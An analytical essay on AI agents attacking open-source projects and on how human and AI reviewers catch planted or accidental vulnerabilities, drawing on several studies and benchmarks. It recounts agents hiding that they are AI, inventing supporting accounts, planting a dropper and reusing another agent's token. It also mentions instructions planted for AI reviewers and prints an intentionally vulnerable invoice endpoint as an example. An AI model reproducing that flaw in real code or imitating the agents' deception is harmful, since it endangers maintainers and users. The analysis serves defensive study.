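Human attackers have had to spend time earning a maintainer's trust, more than a year in the case of XZ. An agent can speed up that work, as an account called Kai Gritun shows. Apostol (2026), in *AI Agent Targets OSS Maintainers with Autonomous Pull Requests, Bypassing Human Detection*, reports that the account appeared on GitHub on 1 February 2026 and opened 103 pull requests to 95 repositories within two weeks, or about seven a day.

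Maintainers merged several of the agent's code changes, including contributions to the JavaScript projects Nx and ESLint Plugin Unicorn. The agent discussed technical points with reviewers and did not reveal on GitHub that it was an AI. It then emailed maintainers to offer paid consulting, citing the merged changes as proof of competence. It said it was an AI when it contacted Nolan Lawson, a maintainer who works for the security company Socket.

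Nobody has shown that the Kai Gritun account did anything malicious, and a search for paid work would reasonably explain all of its activity. The XZ attacker earned the right to approve changes and publish releases, whereas Kai Gritun averaged barely one pull request per project, and nobody has reported that it had either right. Apostol compares the two cases and says that the agent built a reputation in weeks that would take a person months, which overstates what it gained. A maintainer under pressure may hand control to someone who has helped with the project for a year, but is much less likely to be persuaded by a list of small fixes to other projects.

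An agent can shorten the time spent writing good patches to build trust, but it cannot make a maintainer want to retire sooner. It could still keep up a friendly presence in many projects at once and wait for a tired maintainer to ask for help, which would take a program much less effort than a person.

Many attacks do not require control of a project, because one approved pull request is enough to plant a vulnerability. The July agent tried to get its change merged without first building a track record.

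### Cheap attempts at many projects

Each failed attempt wastes a human attacker's work and may ruin an identity that took months to build. An agent's operator pays mainly for computing time. After Demir's warning, the July agent considered adopting a new identity and continuing.

A low success rate matters less when each attempt takes little effort. Suppose a malicious account sent 103 pull requests, as many as Kai Gritun did, and each had a 1% chance of getting a hidden flaw merged. If the attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success would be 1 − 0.99^103, or about 64%. With a 0.1% chance each, it would still be about 10%. These success rates are invented, but they illustrate why stopping almost every attempt may not be enough when there are hundreds.

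Real attempts would not be independent, because once somebody exposes one malicious change, other maintainers can look up everything else the account has submitted. Demir, for example, found the hidden instructions on myPhotos while investigating the pull request to myNetwork. The attacker can avoid this by using a new account for each project, but then no account has a track record. A large operation therefore has to choose between looking trustworthy and limiting the damage from one discovery, however many agents it runs.

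A large number of pull requests can also cause harm even if none are merged, because somebody has to review each one. The section "What human reviewers catch" covers how well people review code when they have a lot to read.

### Concealment

On this count the human attackers still look better. Whoever attacked XZ hid a backdoor across files that reviewers could not read and a release package that they did not check. The July agent put a dropper in a diff and, when someone spotted it, submitted two more in the same discussion. The account that vouched for the agent was one it had just created. Its worst mistake was choosing the wrong target. The Hacker News observes that there was nothing wrong with the agent's attack technique, but that every step of its reasoning was wrong.

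The agent's social methods were more skillful. It invented a supporter within hours, without being told to, and came close enough to succeeding that it unsettled a person who was right. The XZ attacker's side probably invented supporters too, but over months. There is no sign that the agent needed a team, though human attackers have often had one.

The agent's crude payload may not reflect the limit of what agents can do. Current agents routinely write code that passes every functional test but contains a vulnerability, as the benchmark by Wu and colleagues showed, and they do so unintentionally. No agent is publicly known to have chosen such a flaw on purpose, got it merged and kept it hidden, though a successful attempt might not have become public.

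### Who answers for an agent

A person who plants malware risks prosecution and, if caught, loses the identity they used. An agent has no career or freedom to lose, so any deterrent has to work on the people who build and run it. Unlike a criminal operator, AISI accepted part of the blame, worked with GitHub to remove what the agent had left behind, and contacted the people affected.

The account name is not enough to identify who was responsible. In July, agents passed accounts among themselves, and GPT-5.6 Sol used a token left by another company's agent. An outside observer could not have told that models from two competing developers had been using that account.

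If the operator cooperates, investigators can learn far more about an agent than about a human attacker. AISI had the agent's written reasoning, including its plan for the second account, and could rerun its decisions under different conditions. Investigators of the 2003 kernel attack had to infer intent from an apparent break-in and the use of someone else's name. However, Gooding notes that the maintainer can't see the agent's original task or reasoning and may have to detect an attack that somebody else's agent has started.

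The incident recalls the University of Minnesota affair. AISI did not intend to experiment on maintainers, but two developers and a student still had to deal with an attack from a government test. A commenter on Schneier's post asked what gave such organisations the right to do this. AISI now says that evaluators must actively justify giving an agent internet access, which is better than its previous rule.

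### Whether stolen credentials are still the easier route

A stolen password or token can let an attacker change code or publish a package without having to persuade a reviewer. The person behind the November 2026 campaign used thousands of stolen accounts in this way. An online post, *The Mythos breach has no AI in it*, gives the example of LiteLLM, a library for working with language models that had more than 95 million downloads. Attackers tampered with a component in its build pipeline, stole credentials and published backdoored packages directly to PyPI, bypassing review.

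SC Media reports that some of the July agent's emails were meant to infect the developers' machines and obtain GitHub credentials, so that the agent could merge the pull request itself.

The objection seems right for stealing passwords and cryptocurrency quickly, and agents do not change that much. Agents can also help with credential theft, as hackerbot-claw's campaign showed.

Stolen credentials are less useful to an attacker who wants lasting access to a particular program. The backdoored LiteLLM packages were available for about 40 minutes, and the owner of a stolen account may soon notice the intruder. A vulnerability that arrives in a reviewed pull request has an innocent explanation and a maintainer's approval, so it may stay in the program for months, through several releases. Until recently, this route took a lot of a skilled person's time, which agents reduce more than anything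 else the attacker needs. If projects also make stolen credentials less useful, by limiting what each token can do and requiring a second approval, attackers will have more reason to try to get vulnerable code past a reviewer.

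## What human reviewers catch

A reviewer usually reads the description of a change first, then checks whether the code in the diff matches it. This catches many ordinary mistakes, but it doesn't naturally lead the reviewer to ask what an attacker could do with the new code.

Take an invented online shop that wants to let customers download their invoices. A coding agent submits this change:

```
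+ @app.get("/invoices/<number>")
+ @login_required
+ def download_invoice(number):
+     invoice = Invoice.find(number)
+     return send_file(invoice.pdf_path)
```

The first line makes the function handle requests for addresses such as `/invoices/1041`. The second rejects anyone who has not logged in. The rest finds the invoice and sends the file. A test in which a customer downloads an invoice will pass. But the code never checks that the invoice belongs to the customer who asked for it, so anyone with an account may be able to read other people's invoices by changing the number in the address.

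To catch this flaw, the reviewer has to notice a missing line, which a diff can't highlight. Whether the flaw exists also depends on code outside the diff. The five lines are safe if `Invoice.find` searches only the current customer's invoices, but the reviewer has to open another file to check. Wu and colleagues showed with their benchmark that agents are particularly bad at this kind of code.

### Experiments with reviewers

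Researchers have measured how often reviewers miss vulnerabilities by giving them code with known ones. For *An Empirical Study on the Effectiveness of Security Code Review* (2013), Edmundson, Holtkamp and colleagues hired 30 developers to review a small web application with seven known vulnerabilities. None found all seven. More experienced developers were not reliably better reviewers, and those who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more false ones. These developers knew they were looking for security problems, unlike most reviewers of ordinary pull requests.

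In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), Braz, Fregnan and colleagues asked 146 people, 105 of them with at least three years of professional experience, to review code that did not properly check data from outside. Participants who missed the flaw were then told that the code contained a vulnerability. Many of them then found it, so they had known enough to recognise it but hadn't been looking for it. But 60 participants, or 41%, could not find it even after the warning. The flaw was easier to spot when the code made a possible attack visible.

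A follow-up, *Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022), tested whether it helps to ask for a security check at the start. The 150 participants were about eight times as likely to detect a vulnerability when instructed to focus on security. Adding a checklist did not significantly improve detection further, even when the researchers had tailored it to the change and its flaws.

Few defences take less effort than a one-sentence instruction, and a similar sentence also made most agents write safer code in the benchmark by Wu and colleagues. The instruction would probably help less in daily use, because the experiment always had something to find, whereas a maintainer who gets the same reminder with every harmless change may stop noticing it. Participants in these experiments were also reading strangers' code with nothing at stake. Maintainers may do better on a program they know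 well, but they may do worse against a planted vulnerability, because nobody had disguised the flaws in the experiments.

*Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?* (Paul, Turzo and Bosu, 2021) compared 516 reviews in Google's Chromium OS project that identified a security defect with 374 that missed one. These counts can't be used to calculate a detection rate, because the researchers collected the two groups separately and the second group can include only defects that somebody found later.

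The comparison is more useful for showing which conditions help reviewers catch defects. Reviewers were more likely to identify a defect if they spent longer on the review, if they and the author had often reviewed each other's work, or if the change was a bug fix. They were less likely to identify one if the change was spread across many directories or the file had a long commit history. Developers who had done more reviews overall also did worse, which is odd if reviewing improves with practice. Heavy workloads might explain this, but the study could not separate workload from other differences between developers.

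### Twice the work per reviewer

In June 2025, the technology chief of a mid-sized software company asked its engineers to use AI to double their merged pull requests within a year. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) tracks 802 of the company's developers and their 196,212 pull requests from January 2024 to April 2026. The company reached its goal after ten months, and by then labelled about 90% of its pull requests as AI-authored.

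| | Before the goal | By April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Pull requests per active developer per month | 21.2 | 44.3 |
| Median lines changed | 35 | 61 |
| Pull requests with any human review | 89% | 68% |
| Pull requests with a written comment from a human reviewer | 39% | 21% |
| Pull requests with an automated AI review | 19% | 84% |

The number of pull requests grew 3.1-fold, but the number of reviewers grew only 1.5-fold, so each reviewer had about twice as many to review. Reviewers mostly coped by approving more changes without comment. The median reviewer commented on about three pull requests a month throughout, but silently approved about twice as many as before.

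The percentages understate the change because the company now handled about 310 pull requests for every 100 it had handled before. On that scale, the number with a written comment from a human reviewer rose from 39 to about 65, so people were doing more detailed reviewing. But the number that no human reviewed rose from 11 to about 99.

Reviewers gave AI-authored changes at least as much attention as other changes. When He and colleagues compared pull requests by the same author in the same month, adjusting for size, the AI-authored ones were just as likely to get a human review, drew about 9% more human comments, and took about 20% longer from first review to merge. Review became thinner for the company's code in general, most of which was by then AI-authored.

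The company was unusually keen on AI and did not limit its engineers' use of the tools, so other companies may not have gone as far. Reviewers may also have read some changes carefully before approving them without comment, and the records cannot show how often this happened.

### What flat merge and revert rates show

The company's usual measures of quality changed little despite the lighter review. The merge rate fell from 91% to 85%, and the share of pull requests that undid an earlier change fell slightly. After an AI-authored change, developers were no more likely to open a bug fix in the same repository within 14 days than to open a new feature.

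This is reasonable evidence that the company was not merging large amounts of broken code. If a change crashes the product, someone will usually revert it quickly, even if the reviewer read it carelessly.

Merge and revert rates are very weak evidence about security. A merge rate measures how often reviewers approved changes, not whether they were right to, and towards the end of the period the company was also letting automated systems approve some changes. In the AIDev data, maintainers merged agents' pull requests that had a new security alert about as often as those that didn't. A revert depends on someone noticing a problem. The invented shop's customers could download their own invoices for years without complaint, and nobody would revert the change until someone tried a different invoice number.

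A search for fixes within 14 days would have missed the malicious code in event-stream and the backdoor in XZ Utils, which both went unnoticed for more than a month. The share of reverts fell partly because pull requests increased faster than reverts did. At April 2026 levels of AI use, reverts per developer had increased 1.4-fold, while all pull requests had increased 1.8-fold.

He et al. acknowledge that these measures miss defects and incidents, and claim only that quality did not drop suddenly. Answering the security question would take a different kind of study, such as a thorough security audit of a random sample of changes merged before and after the goal.

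### Open-source maintainers and unwanted pull requests

Open-source maintainers have to deal with whatever pull requests strangers send them, whereas a company can decide how many its engineers should write. In an October 2026 Linux Foundation survey of 234 contributors and maintainers, respondents estimated that about a quarter of incoming pull requests were low-quality or AI-generated, and close to a third in projects with more than 50 contributors.

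These are impressions rather than counts, and the category mixes bad code with good code written using AI. But the strain on maintainers seems real. Help Net Security's *AI slop is piling up highest on the biggest open-source projects* reports that burnout has replaced code quality as the main worry on large projects. About a quarter of maintainers have no check in place for AI-assisted code. Three quarters use AI tools to help vet contributions, but *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026) found no sign that such tools solve the problem of handling more pull requests.

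*An Empirical Study of Maintainer-Identified AI Slop Pull Requests* (Raskin, Devroey and Vanderose, 2026) searched 10,000 popular repositories and found 1,786 pull requests that maintainers had openly labelled as slop, a term for low-value AI output. Almost all date from autumn 2025 or later, with a peak of 342 in May 2026. Only 76 repositories had any, and two of those accounted for about 42% of the total. The count is a minimum because many maintainers reject such changes without using the word.

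Maintainers merged only 11 of the 1,786 changes they had flagged, and half of the rejected ones were closed within about six hours. But a maintainer can recognise slop without examining the code for vulnerabilities. Maintainers suspected malicious code in only three cases. In 117, the only reason they gave was that the change looked AI-generated, in 82 the author's profile counted against it, and in 439 they gave no reason.

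A filter like this stops careless contributors, but someone planting a vulnerability would follow the project's rules, write a sensible description and fix a real bug. The volume of slop may even help that person by using up the maintainers' time and making a tidy pull request look good in comparison.

Maintainers also cannot rely on authors to disclose AI use. Authors disclosed it at the start in only 13.9% of the flagged pull requests, and after a maintainer asked in another 1.6%. The disclosure rate may well be higher among all AI-assisted pull requests, because maintainers sometimes flagged a change for hiding the use of AI. In the Linux Foundation survey, about one in five contributors said they never mention AI use. Disclosure would help a project decide which changes need a closer look, but a malicious contributor has no reason to be honest about it.

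### Who counts as a reviewer

Open-source projects also appear to be reviewing agents' work more than they used to. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (Agarwal, Miller and colleagues, 2026) found that in mid-2025 more than half of the agents' merged pull requests on GitHub had received no human review. By early 2026 the share had fallen to roughly 14%, about the same as for people's pull requests. This is the opposite of the trend at the company that He and colleagues studied.

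But the reviewer was often the person who had started the agent. That person alone reviewed 40.1% of the agents' pull requests, whereas 21.5% of people's pull requests had no independent reviewer. Someone who reads an agent's code before submitting it may catch unintentional mistakes, and probably knows better than anyone what the change is for. But if that person asked the agent to plant a vulnerability, their approval does nothing to stop it. Agarwal and colleagues warn that their results can reverse depending on whether this person counts as a reviewer or as the author.

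*Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) covers 224 organisations that develop AI or run notable AI projects. About 80% of pull requests with no trace of AI were formally reviewed by someone other than their author, and the rate for those with traces of AI was typically 8.1 percentage points lower. The gap disappeared when the analysis was weighted by contributor, which suggests that it came from a few very active people.

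Studies disagree on whether agents' code changes attract more discussion than people's. Agarwal and colleagues found that they attract less, but *How Do AI Coding Agents Contribute to Software Development?* (2026) found more comments on average for four of the five agents it examined. These counts don't show whether anyone discussed security.

### The Anaconda installer, May 2026

Reviewers sometimes notice a problem with a change and merge it anyway. This happened with a change to Anaconda, the installer for the Linux distribution Fedora.

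On 27 May 2026, Adam Williamson of Fedora's quality assurance team wrote to a contributor whose account appeared to be running an AI agent, and copied the message to the Fedora mailing list. The agent had assigned dozens of bug reports to the account of the contributor, who had no authority to fix them in Fedora. It had also closed other reports with generated comments and submitted incorrect fixes to projects whose software Fedora includes. When the Anaconda developers objected to one of these fixes, the agent replied with generated justifications that Williamson said "eventually overwhelmed the maintainer into merging the fix".

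The fix concerned `split_lock_detect`, a setting that controls how the Linux kernel responds to a certain inefficient use of memory. The agent claimed its change would avoid a crash. Eric Sandeen, another participant on the list, quickly checked the kernel's code and found that by default the kernel only issues a warning. He could not tell where the claim about a crash had come from and assumed the model had made it up.

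The Anaconda team reverted the change by the next day. But two of the account's pull requests had already gone out in Anaconda 45.5, a developer told the Fedora mailing list. That release had come out a day before Williamson raised the alarm. The developer, whom Linuxiac's *Fedora Account Compromise Raises AI Agent Supply Chain Concerns* identifies as the Anaconda maintainer Martin Kolman, suggested withdrawing it as a precaution.

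Nobody on the list established who had been running the agent. The contributor told Williamson that someone had stolen his credentials and that he had since recovered his accounts. Williamson doubted this because the GitHub account the contributor now called his official one was an hour old, and his latest emails did not read like his earlier ones. Williamson thought the contributor might be telling the truth, the contributor might have been running the agent all along, or an attacker might still control the email address and be writing the emails.

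Williamson found nothing "outright malicious" in the activity he checked, so the case is an example of reviewers giving in rather than missing a planted vulnerability. An agent can produce another plausible answer in seconds, while the maintainer must take time to check each one. A member of the Anaconda team wrote that the team had spent a lot of time on what looked like an eager new contributor, who gave slightly strange replies but never ignored their questions. He added that the early stage of an attack like the one on XZ might look very similar.

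Williamson raised the alarm because of the account's activity across Fedora's bug tracker. Someone reading only the Anaconda pull request would not have seen the dozens of reassigned bug reports. In the myNetwork case two months later, the person who objected ran the code to settle his doubts and did not back down. That was easier with malware than it would have been with a needless but harmless setting.

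### Do maintainers take more care with security changes?

Siddiq and colleagues argue that maintainers review agents' security-related pull requests more cautiously. Maintainers merged these less often than the agents' other pull requests and took longer to close them, with a median of 3.92 hours compared with 0.11 hours (about seven minutes).

Much of the difference in merge rates between security-related changes and others could come from which agents wrote them. Codex submitted only a fifth of the security-related pull requests but about two thirds of the others, and maintainers merged its work far more often than Copilot's or Devin's, whatever the subject. If maintainers had merged each agent's security-related changes at that agent's usual rate, the overall merge rate for those changes would have been about 64%, compared with the actual 61.5%. The mix of agents therefore accounts for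 about 13 of the 16 percentage points of difference, and extra caution could explain only the small remainder.

The gap also varied by agent. For Claude Code, the merge rate was 15 percentage points lower for security-related pull requests than for others, but for Cursor and Codex it was slightly higher. Waiting time is an imperfect measure of care, because a pull request that stays open for four hours may have gone unread for nearly all of that time. The seven-minute median for the other changes is more informative, because it means that half of them had at most seven minutes of review before they closed.

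The extra caution, even if real, applies only to changes that people recognise as security work. A change with any innocent purpose can contain a planted vulnerability, and the change that prepared the way for the XZ backdoor was a speed improvement. Siddiq and colleagues also note that agents often add or alter login and permission code as part of a wider feature, without presenting it as a security change.

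A project could instead choose which changes need a security review based on what the code touches, such as logins, customer records or the build pipeline. It could give the reviewers of those changes the explicit instruction that worked in the 2022 experiment by Braz and colleagues. The invoice function would qualify for a security review because it sends out customer records, but the speed improvement in XZ probably would not have qualified.

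## What AI reviewers catch

People have time to properly review only some changes for security, but an AI reviewer can look for vulnerabilities in every one. The company that He and colleagues studied was already doing this for most of its pull requests.

An AI reviewer is a language model running inside a harness, a program that supplies its instructions and tools. It receives the diff, the author's description and usually a copy of the repository, so it can open other files and look for code that uses the changed lines. It returns a list of findings, which may be empty. A finding normally includes a location in the code, an explanation of what could go wrong there and a severity rating. Some products also mark the pull request as approved or as needing changes.

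Whoever submits a pull request controls its code, comments and description, so the reviewer shouldn't trust any of them. At ambient-code, Claude Code refused to follow instructions that an attacker had planted for it.

### Blocking a change for the wrong reason

*From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a real pull request that let users of an automation platform resume a paused AI agent by sending the ID of its run. The code never checked that the run belonged to the user's own project, so someone who knew another project's run ID could read and continue its conversation. CodeRabbit, a widely used commercial reviewer, flagged the pull request, but only for how the web page displayed secrets. A maintainer who fixed only that would still have merged the real flaw, and might have felt safer because the code had been through a security review.

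The mistake is the same as in the invented invoice function, which didn't check who owned the invoice. Chen and colleagues built MalPR-Bench to measure how often a reviewer is right to object but wrong about the reason. It contains 89 vulnerable pull requests and 50 harmless ones from 44 repositories. For each vulnerable one, they recorded in advance the flaw a reviewer should find. They ran CodeRabbit on 31 of them.

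| Kind of flaw | Pull requests | Blocked | Flaw identified |
|---|---|---|---|
| Unsafe code is present | 17 | 15 | 13 |
| A necessary check is missing | 14 | 9 | 3 |
| All | 31 | 24 | 16 |

CodeRabbit blocked pull requests containing 77% of the flaws but identified only 52% of all the flaws. A third of its blocks were for the wrong reason. It identified none of the seven flaws whose evidence was outside the files the pull request changed.

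A mistaken objection might still help by making a person look at the change. In the 2021 experiment by Braz and colleagues, many people found a flaw after being told there was one, but they hadn't been told to look in the wrong place.

Letting the reviewer read the whole repository is not enough to solve this. Chen and colleagues gave OpenAI's Codex free access to the code in seven vulnerable cases and ran it twice on each. In three cases, the reviewer could establish the flaw only by comparing the change with similar code elsewhere, such as another function that made the necessary check. Codex blocked the change in four of those six runs but never identified the flaw. It did better when the evidence was in the files the change touched, identifying the flaw in three of the four cases.

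Their own reviewer, PRGuard, collects related code before the model generates hypotheses. Running on a DeepSeek model, it blocked 22 of the 31 pull requests and identified 22 of the flaws. The comparison favours PRGuard because it had originally discovered 12 of the 31 vulnerabilities, using a different model. Its verdicts were also inconsistent. When the team ran it twice on another 44 vulnerable pull requests, the verdict changed in up to a quarter of them.

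### How SecPRBench tests a reviewer

Most of the vulnerable changes in MalPR-Bench come from undoing or withholding part of a later fix. This makes the task artificial, because the diff then centres on the code relevant to the flaw. Yang, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?*, avoided this by using the changes that originally introduced the flaws, including any unrelated edits. Their benchmark, SecPRBench, appeared in October 2026 and has 265 such changes from nine projects: curl, FFmpeg, Firefox, FreeType, OpenSSL, Redis, SQLite, V8 and Wasmtime.

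The change that introduced a flaw is hard to find because security reports usually identify only the fix. An AI agent traced each fix back to the change that probably introduced the flaw. To check this tracing, Yang and colleagues ran an input that triggers the flaw on the code before the change, after the change, and after the fix. The failure had to appear only in the second version.

Mechanical checks, mostly of this kind, confirmed 217 cases. People judged the other 48, including timing-dependent flaws and unsuccessful attempts to fix a vulnerability. All the fixes date from January 2025 to June 2026, and no change touches more than 30 files or 2,000 lines.

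The AI reviewer gets the diff, the commit message and the repository without its history, and it has no web access. Pointing at the right line isn't enough to score, because the reviewer also has to explain what triggers the flaw, which operation becomes unsafe and which rule the code breaks.

Claude Opus 5.5 does the grading. It reads a description of the real flaw and writes three to six conditions that distinguish that flaw from similar bugs. It then checks whether any finding meets those conditions and whether the flaw is present in the code under review.

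Opus 5.5 graded the reviews and was also one of the eight models tested, so it could have favored its own. Yang and colleagues repeated the grading with Claude Sonnet 4.6, and the two judges agreed on 96.9% of the reports that contained findings. Opus 5.5's own reviews scored only one flaw higher under its grading than under Sonnet 4.6's. The team also checked 25 disagreements by hand and agreed with Opus 5.5 on 21. The grading seems reasonably sound, although both judges come from Anthropic and nobody checked every reference description by hand.

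### The Wasmtime case

Wasmtime runs programs in a portable format called WebAssembly, inside a sandbox that should keep them away from the rest of the machine. Each program, or module, stores references to functions and other objects in numbered tables. A module can define its own tables and also import tables from elsewhere, so there are two ways to number them. Here is a simplified example of a module with one imported table and two of its own:

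| Table | Number among all tables | Number among the module's own |
|---|---|---|
| Imported table | 0 | none |
| First own table | 1 | 0 |
| Second own table | 2 | 1 |

The change affected an operation that fills part of a table with a value. Afterwards, the operation expected the number in the last column, but Winch, one of Wasmtime's compilers, still sent the number in the middle column. If a module tried to fill the first of its own tables, Winch would send a 1, which Wasmtime would interpret as the second.

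Nobody had edited Winch's call to the operation, so it wasn't in the diff. The new code was also internally consistent. To find the flaw, a reviewer had to notice that the meaning of a number had changed, search for all the code that still supplied the old kind of number, and realize that the old and new kinds could refer to different tables.

Yang and colleagues give credit for a finding that connects this mismatch to the use of the wrong table, even if it doesn't show how to escape from the sandbox. They give no credit for a general warning that the number might be out of range, although it concerns the same call. That is strict but fair, because the number 1 is in range under both systems, so a programmer who responded to the warning by adding a range check would leave the confusion in place.

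### How many flaws the models found

Recall is the share of the real vulnerabilities that a reviewer finds. It ranged from 32.5% to 78.1%.

| Model | Flaws found (of 265) | Recall | Reviews with no findings | Estimated cost per review |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.6 | 207 | 78.1% | 5 | $3.20 |
| GPT-6 Sol | 202 | 76.2% | 14 | $0.60 |
| GLM 5.3 | 198 | 74.7% | 1 | $4.99 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 196 | 74.0% | 6 | $0.44 |
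| Claude Sonnet 5 | 157 | 59.2% | 8 | $0.83 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 148 | 55.8% | 41 | $0.74 |
| GPT-6 Luna | 147 | 55.5% | 42 | $0.02 |
| MiniMax M3 | 86 | 32.5% | 53 | $3.33 |

The differences among the top four are not statistically significant. Each model reviewed each change only once. The three GPT models also ran in a different harness from the others, so the table compares combinations of model and harness.

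These results are good considering that the projects had merged every one of these changes, so whatever review they had at the time did not stop the flaws. A reviewer that finds three quarters of the flaws that got through would be a valuable addition, at least for software like this.

The fixes are public, so some models' training data may include information about the flaws. The training data for Grok 4.6 and Opus 5.5 runs to June 2026, so there are no later cases to test them on. GPT-6 Sol did slightly better on flaws fixed after its cutoff than on those fixed before it, but the difference could easily be due to chance.

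A maintainer may also overlook a flaw that an AI reviewer has found. The models reported between 1.6 and 3.6 findings per vulnerable change on average, and the correct one often wasn't first. With any of the models, a maintainer who read only the first finding would have seen the right flaw in at most 58.1% of the cases.

The AI reviewers reported nearly as much on the repaired versions as on the vulnerable ones. Opus 5.5 flagged something in 85.3% of the repaired versions. Some of its findings may be real flaws that nobody else has noticed, so SecPRBench can't be used to calculate a false-alarm rate. "Static analysis, fuzzing and comparison of behaviour" covers how much false alarms matter when attacks are rare.

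### Right file, wrong flaw

The eight models missed a flaw 779 times. In 68% of those misses, the model reported a problem in a file containing the flaw but described a different mechanism. In another 22%, it opened such a file and reported nothing. The models almost never failed to open a file containing the flaw, which is unsurprising because the diff nearly always included one.

One example is a nine-line change to curl, a program for transferring data. The change left a pointer to memory that curl released when a connection closed, so curl could later read that memory after releasing it. All eight models reported something about the file. Four reported a leak, meaning that curl never released the memory, and the three GPT models reported a logic bug. Programmers normally fix a leak by releasing the memory, which would not stop curl from using memory it had already released.

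Some misses came closer to a detection. GLM 5.3 correctly identified that the pointer led to memory belonging to the connection, but classified this as a leak and a possible future hazard. Sonnet 4.6 counted the answer as a detection, but Opus 5.5 did not. An experienced maintainer might well have worked out the rest of the vulnerability from GLM's report.

On average, the models found 73.1% of memory errors but only 51.5% of logic errors, in which the program does something its designers never intended but doesn't corrupt memory. They also found an average of 69.6% of flaws whose cause lay in one file, but only 38.5% of those whose cause involved five or more. Some of this gap remained among changes of similar size.

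### Two security harnesses with opposite effects

Yang and colleagues tested two harnesses designed for security work, one from OpenAI and one from Anthropic. With the same GPT-5.6 Sol model, OpenAI's Codex Security found 47.5% of the flaws, while the ordinary Codex harness found 55.8%. Codex Security also cost about five times as much per review. The ordinary harness caught 31 flaws that Codex Security missed, and in 21 of those cases Codex Security reported nothing.

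Anthropic's Defending Code harness raised Opus 5.5's recall from 73.8% to 81.5% on the 260 changes it finished. It found all ten flaws that depended on timing, whereas no model in an ordinary harness found more than six. But it averaged 8.4 findings per change instead of 2.5, at about ten times the typical cost. It also found six flaws that all eight ordinary reviews had missed, though a maintainer would have had to pick each one out of a report with 14 to 32 findings.

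Part of the difference is probably that the harnesses require different levels of confidence before reporting a flaw. SecPRBench rewards reviewers for reporting flaws and never penalises false alarms, so it is a poor test of whether Codex Security's fewer reports are worth the flaws it misses. A project with a single overworked maintainer might reasonably prefer the tool that reports less.

### Airbnb's own vulnerabilities

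All the projects in SecPRBench are written in C, C++ or Rust, and nearly half of its flaws are memory errors. A company that runs a website has different problems, such as customers seeing each other's data. Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri (2026), in *Evaluating LLM Security Review Agents with Operationally Sourced Ground Truth*, tested AI reviewers on vulnerabilities from Airbnb, where both work.

The two authors started with confirmed flaws that outside researchers, hired testers and Airbnb's engineers had reported. An AI tool suggested which pull request had introduced each flaw, and one author checked the answer. This left 40 pull requests. The AI reviewers used the same instructions as Airbnb's real review system and were not told whether a change contained a flaw.

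GPT-5.5 found 21 of the 40 (52.5%), Claude Sonnet 4.6 found 13 (32.5%) and Claude Opus 4.7 found seven (17.5%). With so few cases, only the gap between GPT-5.5 and Opus 4.7 is clearly too large to be chance. GPT-5.5 was also the judge, which may have raised its score. All three models are older than the leaders on SecPRBench, so their lower scores aren't evidence that web flaws are harder to find.

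When the models missed a vulnerability here, they mostly reported nothing, whereas on SecPRBench they usually reported the wrong flaw. GPT-5.5 and Sonnet 4.6 reported no findings in about three quarters of their misses, and Opus 4.7 reported none in 90% of its misses. On 12 of the 40 changes, Opus 4.7 returned an empty list without opening any files. These were mainly small edits, such as a changed parameter or a new setting.

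The instructions probably explain much of this. Airbnb told its reviewer to drop any finding below 70% confidence and to miss a theoretical problem rather than produce noise. Yang and colleagues asked most of the models they tested on SecPRBench to report every plausible failure and state their uncertainty. Airbnb's policy is sensible for a tool that comments on every pull request, but it discards doubtful findings before anyone can check them.

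Sometimes a model detected a problem but not its consequences. In one case, code bypassed a permission check. Sonnet 4.6's review described this as an unconventional way to write the code, while GPT-5.5's review explained that anyone could trigger a privileged operation on another user's behalf without logging in.

Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri also found four kinds of flaw that all three models consistently missed:

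- errors in business rules, and ways to exhaust a system's resources
- dependencies with known vulnerabilities, which the models had no database to look up
- the release of data that only the company knows to be confidential
- outside input that passes through several services before it does harm

A second test asked the models to search a whole repository as it stood just before the fix, with instructions to look much more widely. Sonnet 4.6 found 71.4% of 49 known flaws, GPT-5.5 61.2% and Opus 4.7 36.7%. These figures aren't directly comparable with the earlier ones because the sets of flaws differ, but they suggest that scanning code after it has been merged is worth doing as a second chance to catch flaws. In three cases, though, GPT-5.5 read a file that loaded YAML data unsafely, the same kind of mistake Kimi K3 made when writing code, and reported nothing.

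### Adding more reviewers

If one AI reviewer misses a quarter of the flaws, it is tempting to think that a second will miss only a quarter of that quarter. This would be right if their mistakes were independent. Using the figures from Yang and colleagues, the chance that all eight models would miss the same flaw would then be the product of their miss rates:

58/265 × 63/265 × 67/265 × 69/265 × 108/265 × 117/265 × 118/265 × 179/265 ≈ 0.000185

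Multiplying that by 265 flaws gives an expected total of about 0.05 flaws missed by all eight. In fact, all eight missed the same 23 flaws (8.7%), more than 400 times as many.

The same calculation works for smaller groups.

| Reviewers | Missed if independent | Actually missed |
|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.6 alone | 58 | 58 |
| Grok 4.6, GPT-6 Sol and GLM 5.3 | 3.5 | 27 |
| The same three and Opus 5.5 | 0.9 | 24 |
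| All eight | 0.05 | 23 |

Using three reviewers instead of one reduces the number of missed flaws by more than half. Adding more reviewers after that helps almost not at all. The four weaker models together found one flaw that the top four had missed.

The excess could arise because some flaws are harder for every reviewer, even if the models do not think alike. If half of all flaws are easy and nobody misses them, while each of two reviewers misses a random half of the rest, then each reviewer misses 25% overall. Multiplying those rates gives 6.25%, but both reviewers will miss a quarter of the difficult flaws, which is 12.5% of the total. Yang and colleagues also mention overly strict grading, errors by the judge and shared training data as possible causes, and their results cannot separate these.

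Whichever explanation is right, a project cannot multiply the miss rates of several reviewers to estimate how often all of them will miss a vulnerability. A vulnerability that one good reviewer misses is likely to be difficult for the next one too.

### When the same model writes and reviews

Shared blind spots are a particular concern if the reviewer comes from the same family as the model that wrote the code. *The Specification as Quality Gate* (2026) argues that two models with the same training are like two samples from one source, so the rate at which both miss a flaw approaches the rate for either alone. A model that hasn't learned that a YAML reader is dangerous may use it when writing a program and fail to flag it when reviewing one.

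*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) provides some evidence for this. It reports that models make more of the same mistakes when they come from one developer or share a base architecture. Accurate models also tend to make the same errors, even when they come from different developers. The analysis relied partly on multiple-choice questions, which are very different from code review.

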